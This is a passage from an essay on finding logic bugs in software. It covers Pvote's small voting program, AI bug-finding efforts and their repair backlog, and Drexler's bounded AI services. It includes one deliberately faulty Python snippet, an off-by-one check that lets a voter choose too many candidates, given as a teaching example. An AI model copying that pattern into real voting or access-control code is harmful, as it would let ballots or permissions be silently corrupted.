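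Once somebody has stated a rule, a better design can often make it harder to break. Here the developers could replace `store` with `login.videos()`, a reference that leads only to the logged-in customer's videos. Then no mistake in `get_thumbnail` could give access to video 812, and a reviewer would only have to check the short function that builds the reference.

### When the program works as designed

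Some harm involves no bug. The service's support staff need to open customers' videos to investigate complaints, and an employee might use that access to look up a neighbour. Software components can misuse their access in the same way. The malicious version of the Solana library stole private keys using the same access to keys and servers that the legitimate version needed.

Narrower rights reduce this harm. The service could let staff watch a video only while a complaint about it is open, and notify the customer each time. A nosy employee could then see far fewer videos, but someone would still have to judge whether each viewing was justified.

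The people who grant rights can also make the wrong decision. Suppose the developers add a sharing feature and amend their rule so that customers may see any video whose owner *has shared* it with them. A hospital shares a training video with a nurse, then withdraws the share after the nurse leaves for another job. It is still true that the hospital has shared the video, so a program that keeps showing it to the nurse obeys the rule, and a proof would confirm this.

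### Experts and 460 lines of Python

Logic bugs should be easier to find in a very small program written in a safe language. Ka-Ping Yee's Pvote, a program for voting machines, is a good test of this idea. It has 460 lines of Python, a memory-safe language, while commercial voting machines ran tens of thousands of lines of code when it was written.

Yee kept Pvote short by moving most of the user interface work to a separate program. The software in an ordinary voting machine has to lay out the names, draw the buttons and respond to the voter, all on election day. With Pvote, the separate program does the design work in advance and produces a ballot file, which contains pictures of the screens, sound recordings for voters who can't see them, and a table of what each touch or key press does. Pvote only has to show the pictures, play the recordings, follow the table and keep track of the voter's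 choices.

The ballot file can still contain a serious mistake, such as a button under one candidate's name that selects another. But officials can publish the file before the election, and anyone who tries out the ballot can find that mistake without reading any code.

In a study with David Wagner, one of the DarpaBrowser's reviewers, Yee had security experts review a version of Pvote with bugs planted in it. They found the easier bugs but missed the hardest. According to Financial Cryptography (2013), Wagner later reconstructed a version with a planted bug and invited programmers to look for it, on condition that they didn't post the answer.

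An invented example shows how small such a bug can be. In this code, `limit` is the number of candidates a voter may choose:

```python
if len(chosen) <= limit:
    chosen.append(candidate)
```

The comparison should be `<`. As written, the code lets a voter select two candidates in a contest that allows only one, which would normally spoil the vote. Python runs the code without an error, and anyone who tests the machine by choosing one candidate per contest will see nothing wrong.

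Pvote's small size helped its reviewers, who could read all 460 lines. But logic bugs often depend on how two distant lines interact, and there are 105,570 possible pairs. Because Pvote is written in Python, the reviewers didn't have to look for memory faults in Pvote itself, but they still had to look for them in the Python interpreter, a much larger program written in C.

One program and a few experts are too small a sample to show how often reviewers miss logic bugs. People who plant bugs also hide them carefully, so most honest mistakes are probably easier to find. But a dishonest developer would hide a bug just as carefully, and voting software has to be safe from such developers.

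AI provers could probably verify 460 lines of code today, given a specification. Part of that specification would come from election law. For example, if a voter walks away before finishing, some American states tell poll workers to cast the ballot and others tell them to cancel it.

### Searching without an alarm

In software testing, an *oracle* is a method for deciding whether a program has behaved incorrectly. AddressSanitizer, which detects invalid memory accesses while a program runs, is an excellent oracle for memory faults. Carlini and colleagues say that all 112 bugs an earlier Claude model reported in Firefox were real, and they credit tools of this kind.

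Logic bugs don't set off such an alarm. The faulty `get_thumbnail` returns a valid picture, and only someone who knows whose video it came from can tell that something is wrong. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) defines logic bugs as behaviour that conflicts with a program's implicit rules. A tool can't simply look these rules up because they are implicit.

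The study, published on 2 December, compared four ways of using language models to find these bugs. The researchers tested the methods on past logic bugs and also looked for unknown ones in current software. The simplest methods worked best, and small projects can easily copy them. This result suggests that success depends more on how well the model understands code than on the tooling around it.

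*Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (Pogorelec, 2026) lists findings in macOS, Caliptra, eBPF and the Rust compiler. Caliptra is an open-source design for the part of a data-centre chip that checks the chip's firmware when the chip starts. Other software relies on Caliptra, the eBPF verifier and the Rust compiler for its safety, so a logic bug in one of them can weaken the guarantee for every program that depends on it.

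Reports are slow to confirm without an oracle. Suppose an AI reviewer produces 1,000 reports. If they concern memory faults, a computer can rerun them all overnight and discard those that cause no invalid access. But if they concern logic bugs, and a person needs half an hour to check each one, the job takes 500 hours, or more than twelve working weeks.

It also makes the search harder. A model looking for memory faults can try an input, check whether it sets off the alarm, and try again. With logic bugs, the model has to decide whether an odd result is a fault or intended behavior. This is easier for attackers, because someone who wants other people's videos knows immediately when they have one.

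Developers can build the attacker's test themselves by creating two test customers, one with only plain red videos and one with only plain blue ones, then logging in as the red customer and sending random requests. Any blue thumbnail reveals a bug. If they pick the video and customer number in each request at random from both customers, about one in four requests will pair a blue video with the blue customer's number, so the test would expose the fault in `get_thumbnail` within seconds.

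*How To Fuzz for Logic Bugs?* (Drescher, 2026) applies this approach to site isolation, the browser rule that keeps different websites in separate processes. Drescher observes that memory-safe languages are shifting attention towards logic bugs. A purpose-built oracle makes checking one rule a narrow task. But it covers only the rule somebody thought of, so the red and blue videos wouldn't reveal that the nurse still has access.

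### What AI reviewers can find

Anthropic's Mythos Preview model was already finding logic bugs in April 2026. Carlini and colleagues report that it found several ways to bypass the login in web applications. Some let a stranger become an administrator, and others let a stranger into an account without its password or two-factor code. The researchers gave no details because the developers hadn't yet fixed any of these bugs. The model also found flaws in widely used cryptography libraries that could let an attacker forge certificates or decrypt private messages.

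Carlini and colleagues say that the model reliably distinguishes what code should do from what it does. For example, it infers that a login function should admit only authorised users, even if the code contains a way to bypass the login. They add that they can't confirm the logic bugs it reports with the near-certainty they have for memory faults.

A login function has much the same purpose everywhere, so a model can learn it from other programs. But a hospital's own arrangements determine whether a former employee should still see a training video, and those arrangements may not appear anywhere in the code. If they don't, a model can't work them out by reading more carefully and has to get them from someone who knows.

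AI reviewers have a clearer advantage in how much code they can read. Carlini and colleagues point out that a model can search files that people skip because "obviously someone would have checked that before." Mythos Preview found a 17-year-old flaw in the operating system FreeBSD that let anyone on the internet take complete control of a machine running its file-sharing service. It did this and wrote the attack without human help after the initial request. A thousand runs over OpenBSD cost less than $20,000 and produced several dozen findings besides the 27-year-old flaw.

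Models' scores on CyberGym, a benchmark for finding vulnerabilities, rose from under 20 percent at the beginning of 2025 to over 85 percent in 2026, according to Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026).

Yet no reviewer finds everything. *Fuzzers vs. AI* (Groß, 2026) compared two tools that Google runs on V8, the JavaScript engine in Chrome. In six months, the AI reviewer BigSleep found 45 vulnerabilities and the fuzzer Fuzzilli found 37, and only 25 percent of the bugs overlapped. Further experiments suggested that both tools could find about 60 percent. On either figure, each tool misses many vulnerabilities that the other can find, and there may be others that neither can. Groß recommends using both, which makes sense for reducing the number of flaws but wouldn't show that V8 is secure.

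### Repairs fall behind

Finding a flaw protects people only once someone fixes it. In April 2026 Anthropic launched Project Glasswing, which gives selected companies and open-source developers access to Mythos models so they can find flaws in important software.

The security company VulnCheck counted 217 flaws marked fixed in Anthropic's public ledger as it stood on 2 November, along with 4,866 more that maintainers had received, 1,654 duplicates and 419 entries that Anthropic had withdrawn (Poireault, 2026, *Anthropic's Glasswing Finds Many Security Flaws Yet Delivers Few Fixes*). According to VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026), Anthropic's total number of findings had risen by 11,813 since early September, and the number marked fixed by 15.

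These figures probably understate the repairs. Anthropic counts 629 fixes, almost three times as many, and VulnCheck attributes 442 entries in the main public catalogue of vulnerabilities to Anthropic. KIberblick's *Glasswing* (2026) compared VulnCheck's analysis with Anthropic's dashboard and concluded that the criticism was partly right and partly based on a misreading. It also notes that the ledger covers only open-source software, so it omits any flaws that companies such as Microsoft and Cisco find and quietly fix in their own products. But even 629 fixes cover fewer than one in eight of the flaws Anthropic had reported.

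Human review is the bottleneck. By October Anthropic had more than 29,000 candidate vulnerabilities, but its staff and contractors had reviewed only about 6,000. It began sending unverified reports to maintainers who agreed to receive them, which moves the checking to people who are often volunteers. VulnCheck describes 34 reports about curl, a data-transfer tool included in many other products. Curl's developers decided that 19 weren't vulnerabilities and that six were of low severity, and they were still assessing the other nine.

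Large companies struggle as well. ProPublica's *Anthropic’s New AI Model Can Identify More Software Bugs Than Ever* (2026) describes dozens of Microsoft engineers and managers meeting in May to discuss the weaknesses that Mythos had found in their code and that they were rushing to fix.

AI can also write patches, but a patch that stops one attack may leave the underlying flaw in place. In *Frontier Models’ Vulnerability Patches are Often F.L.A.W.E.D*, Mierczuk, Michaels and Hoodlet asked two leading models of mid-2026 to patch six complex vulnerabilities. They counted a patch as successful only if it closed every known route of attack and didn't wrongly change the program's behaviour. Both models had a low success rate. Some patches added a fragile check that passed the tests without removing the flaw, and others subtly changed what the program did. Newer models may do better, but whoever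 approves a patch still has to know what the program should keep doing.

The backlog strengthens the case for structural constraints, because one design change can deal with many flaws at once. If the thumbnail service's decoder contains fifty memory faults, fixing them individually takes a report, an assessment and a patch for each. A sandbox limits the damage from all fifty, including those nobody has found.

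### Drexler's bounded services

Eric Drexler argues that this kind of work doesn't require a single AI system with general intelligence and wide freedom to act. Drexler's 2019 report *Reframing Superintelligence* proposes dividing the work of advanced AI among services that each have a defined task and limited time and resources. In security, one service might write code while others search it for flaws, prove theorems about it or look for gaps in the specification. People would make the important decisions, and no service would need long-term goals.

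Anthropic's method for finding bugs already works somewhat like this. One copy of the model ranks a project's files from 1 to 5 by how likely they are to contain interesting flaws. Other copies then work on one file each, in a container without internet access. A final copy judges whether each reported bug is real and important.

The same general-purpose model does all these jobs. Carlini and colleagues say its ability to find and exploit vulnerabilities came from general improvements in coding, reasoning and autonomy, not from training specific to that task. Their example supports Drexler's claim that the tasks can be bounded, but it gives no reason to think that a system with narrow knowledge could perform them.

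The counter-argument to Drexler is that judging intent and requirements takes open-ended knowledge of people and institutions. Suppose a school uses the thumbnail service to share videos with parents, and a father asks for the recording of the school play. Normally he should get it, but a court may have barred him from contact with his daughter, and the school office may know this weeks before anyone updates the database. Another child in the play may be living with foster parents whose address is secret, and the video may show which school that child attends. A software expert who knew nothing about families would approve a rule that gives every listed parent every video.

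Nobody could write a complete list of what the reviewer needs to know, because the next customer might be a law firm, whose requirements would depend on professional secrecy, or a hospice, whose requirements would depend on how people treat recordings of someone who has died.

Drexler's report anticipates part of this objection. It distinguishes broad knowledge from broad freedom to act, and suggests that machine learning can produce models that predict what people would approve of. A service could know a great deal about families and courts but only mark doubtful lines in a draft specification. This is a good answer to the worry that security will require a powerful AI agent with goals of its own.

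Simple, specialised checkers would not be enough, because the service that marks doubtful lines would have to understand people about as broadly as a good human reviewer does. Its answers would also be hard to check. No program can reject bad advice about what a school owes to parents the way a small program can reject an invalid proof from an untrusted AI, so people would have to judge the advice themselves.

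### Knowing the purpose and predicting the attacker

The school's problem is difficult, but it doesn't require foreseeing whatever an inventive attacker might try. A reviewer can decide that the father shouldn't have the video without knowing how he would try to get it. However clever the father is, he can't change what the school ought to allow. The reviewer can also ask for help, because the school, its lawyers and the other parents all want the rule to be right.

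The work that remains after the structural constraints needs these two kinds of judgement in different proportions:

| Remaining task | Knowing what the system is for | Predicting an attacker |
|---|---|---|
| Writing the rules for who may see what | Essential | Occasionally useful |
| Deciding which rights a component gets | Essential | Unnecessary if the reviewer assumes the component is hostile |
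| Finding code that breaks a written rule | Needed to understand the rule | Unnecessary with a proof, useful without one |
| Approving a repair | Essential | Needed unless a mechanical check covers the flaw |
| Choosing which flaws to fix first | Needed to judge the damage | Needed to judge the likelihood |
| Detecting misuse of rights that someone needs | Essential | Essential |
| Testing the assumptions behind a proof or sandbox | Less important | Essential |

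Writing rules sometimes takes a little imagination about attackers, because a feature that looks harmless can reveal private information. When someone mistypes their email address on a login page, a message that no account exists for it is helpful. On an addiction clinic's website, the same message lets an employer find out which of its staff are patients by entering their addresses. A designer who thinks only of honest users could easily miss this. A general rule that strangers may learn nothing about who has an account would prevent the leak, and the designer could adopt it without having thought of the employer.

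Such shortcuts help less with the assumptions behind proofs and sandboxes. To discover Rowhammer, researchers had to investigate what memory chips do when someone uses them in a way that no ordinary program would, rather than reason from the chips' purpose. This work is as open-ended as any other search for attacks, but a few specialists can do it for every system that uses the same processor or kernel.

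Detecting misuse is harder to share. If the service raises an alarm when an employee opens 50 videos in a day, a dishonest employee who knows the threshold will open 49. Whoever sets the alarm has to think about how people will avoid it and know what honest support work looks like, which differs between companies.

Account recovery combines the same two difficulties. A customer calls to say that she has lost her phone, can't read her old email and needs her videos for a funeral tomorrow. She may be telling the truth, or she may be an impostor with a moving story. The service can avoid judging her story by sending recovery links only to the address on file. No caller can then persuade an employee to hand over the account, but some real customers will lose their videos for good.
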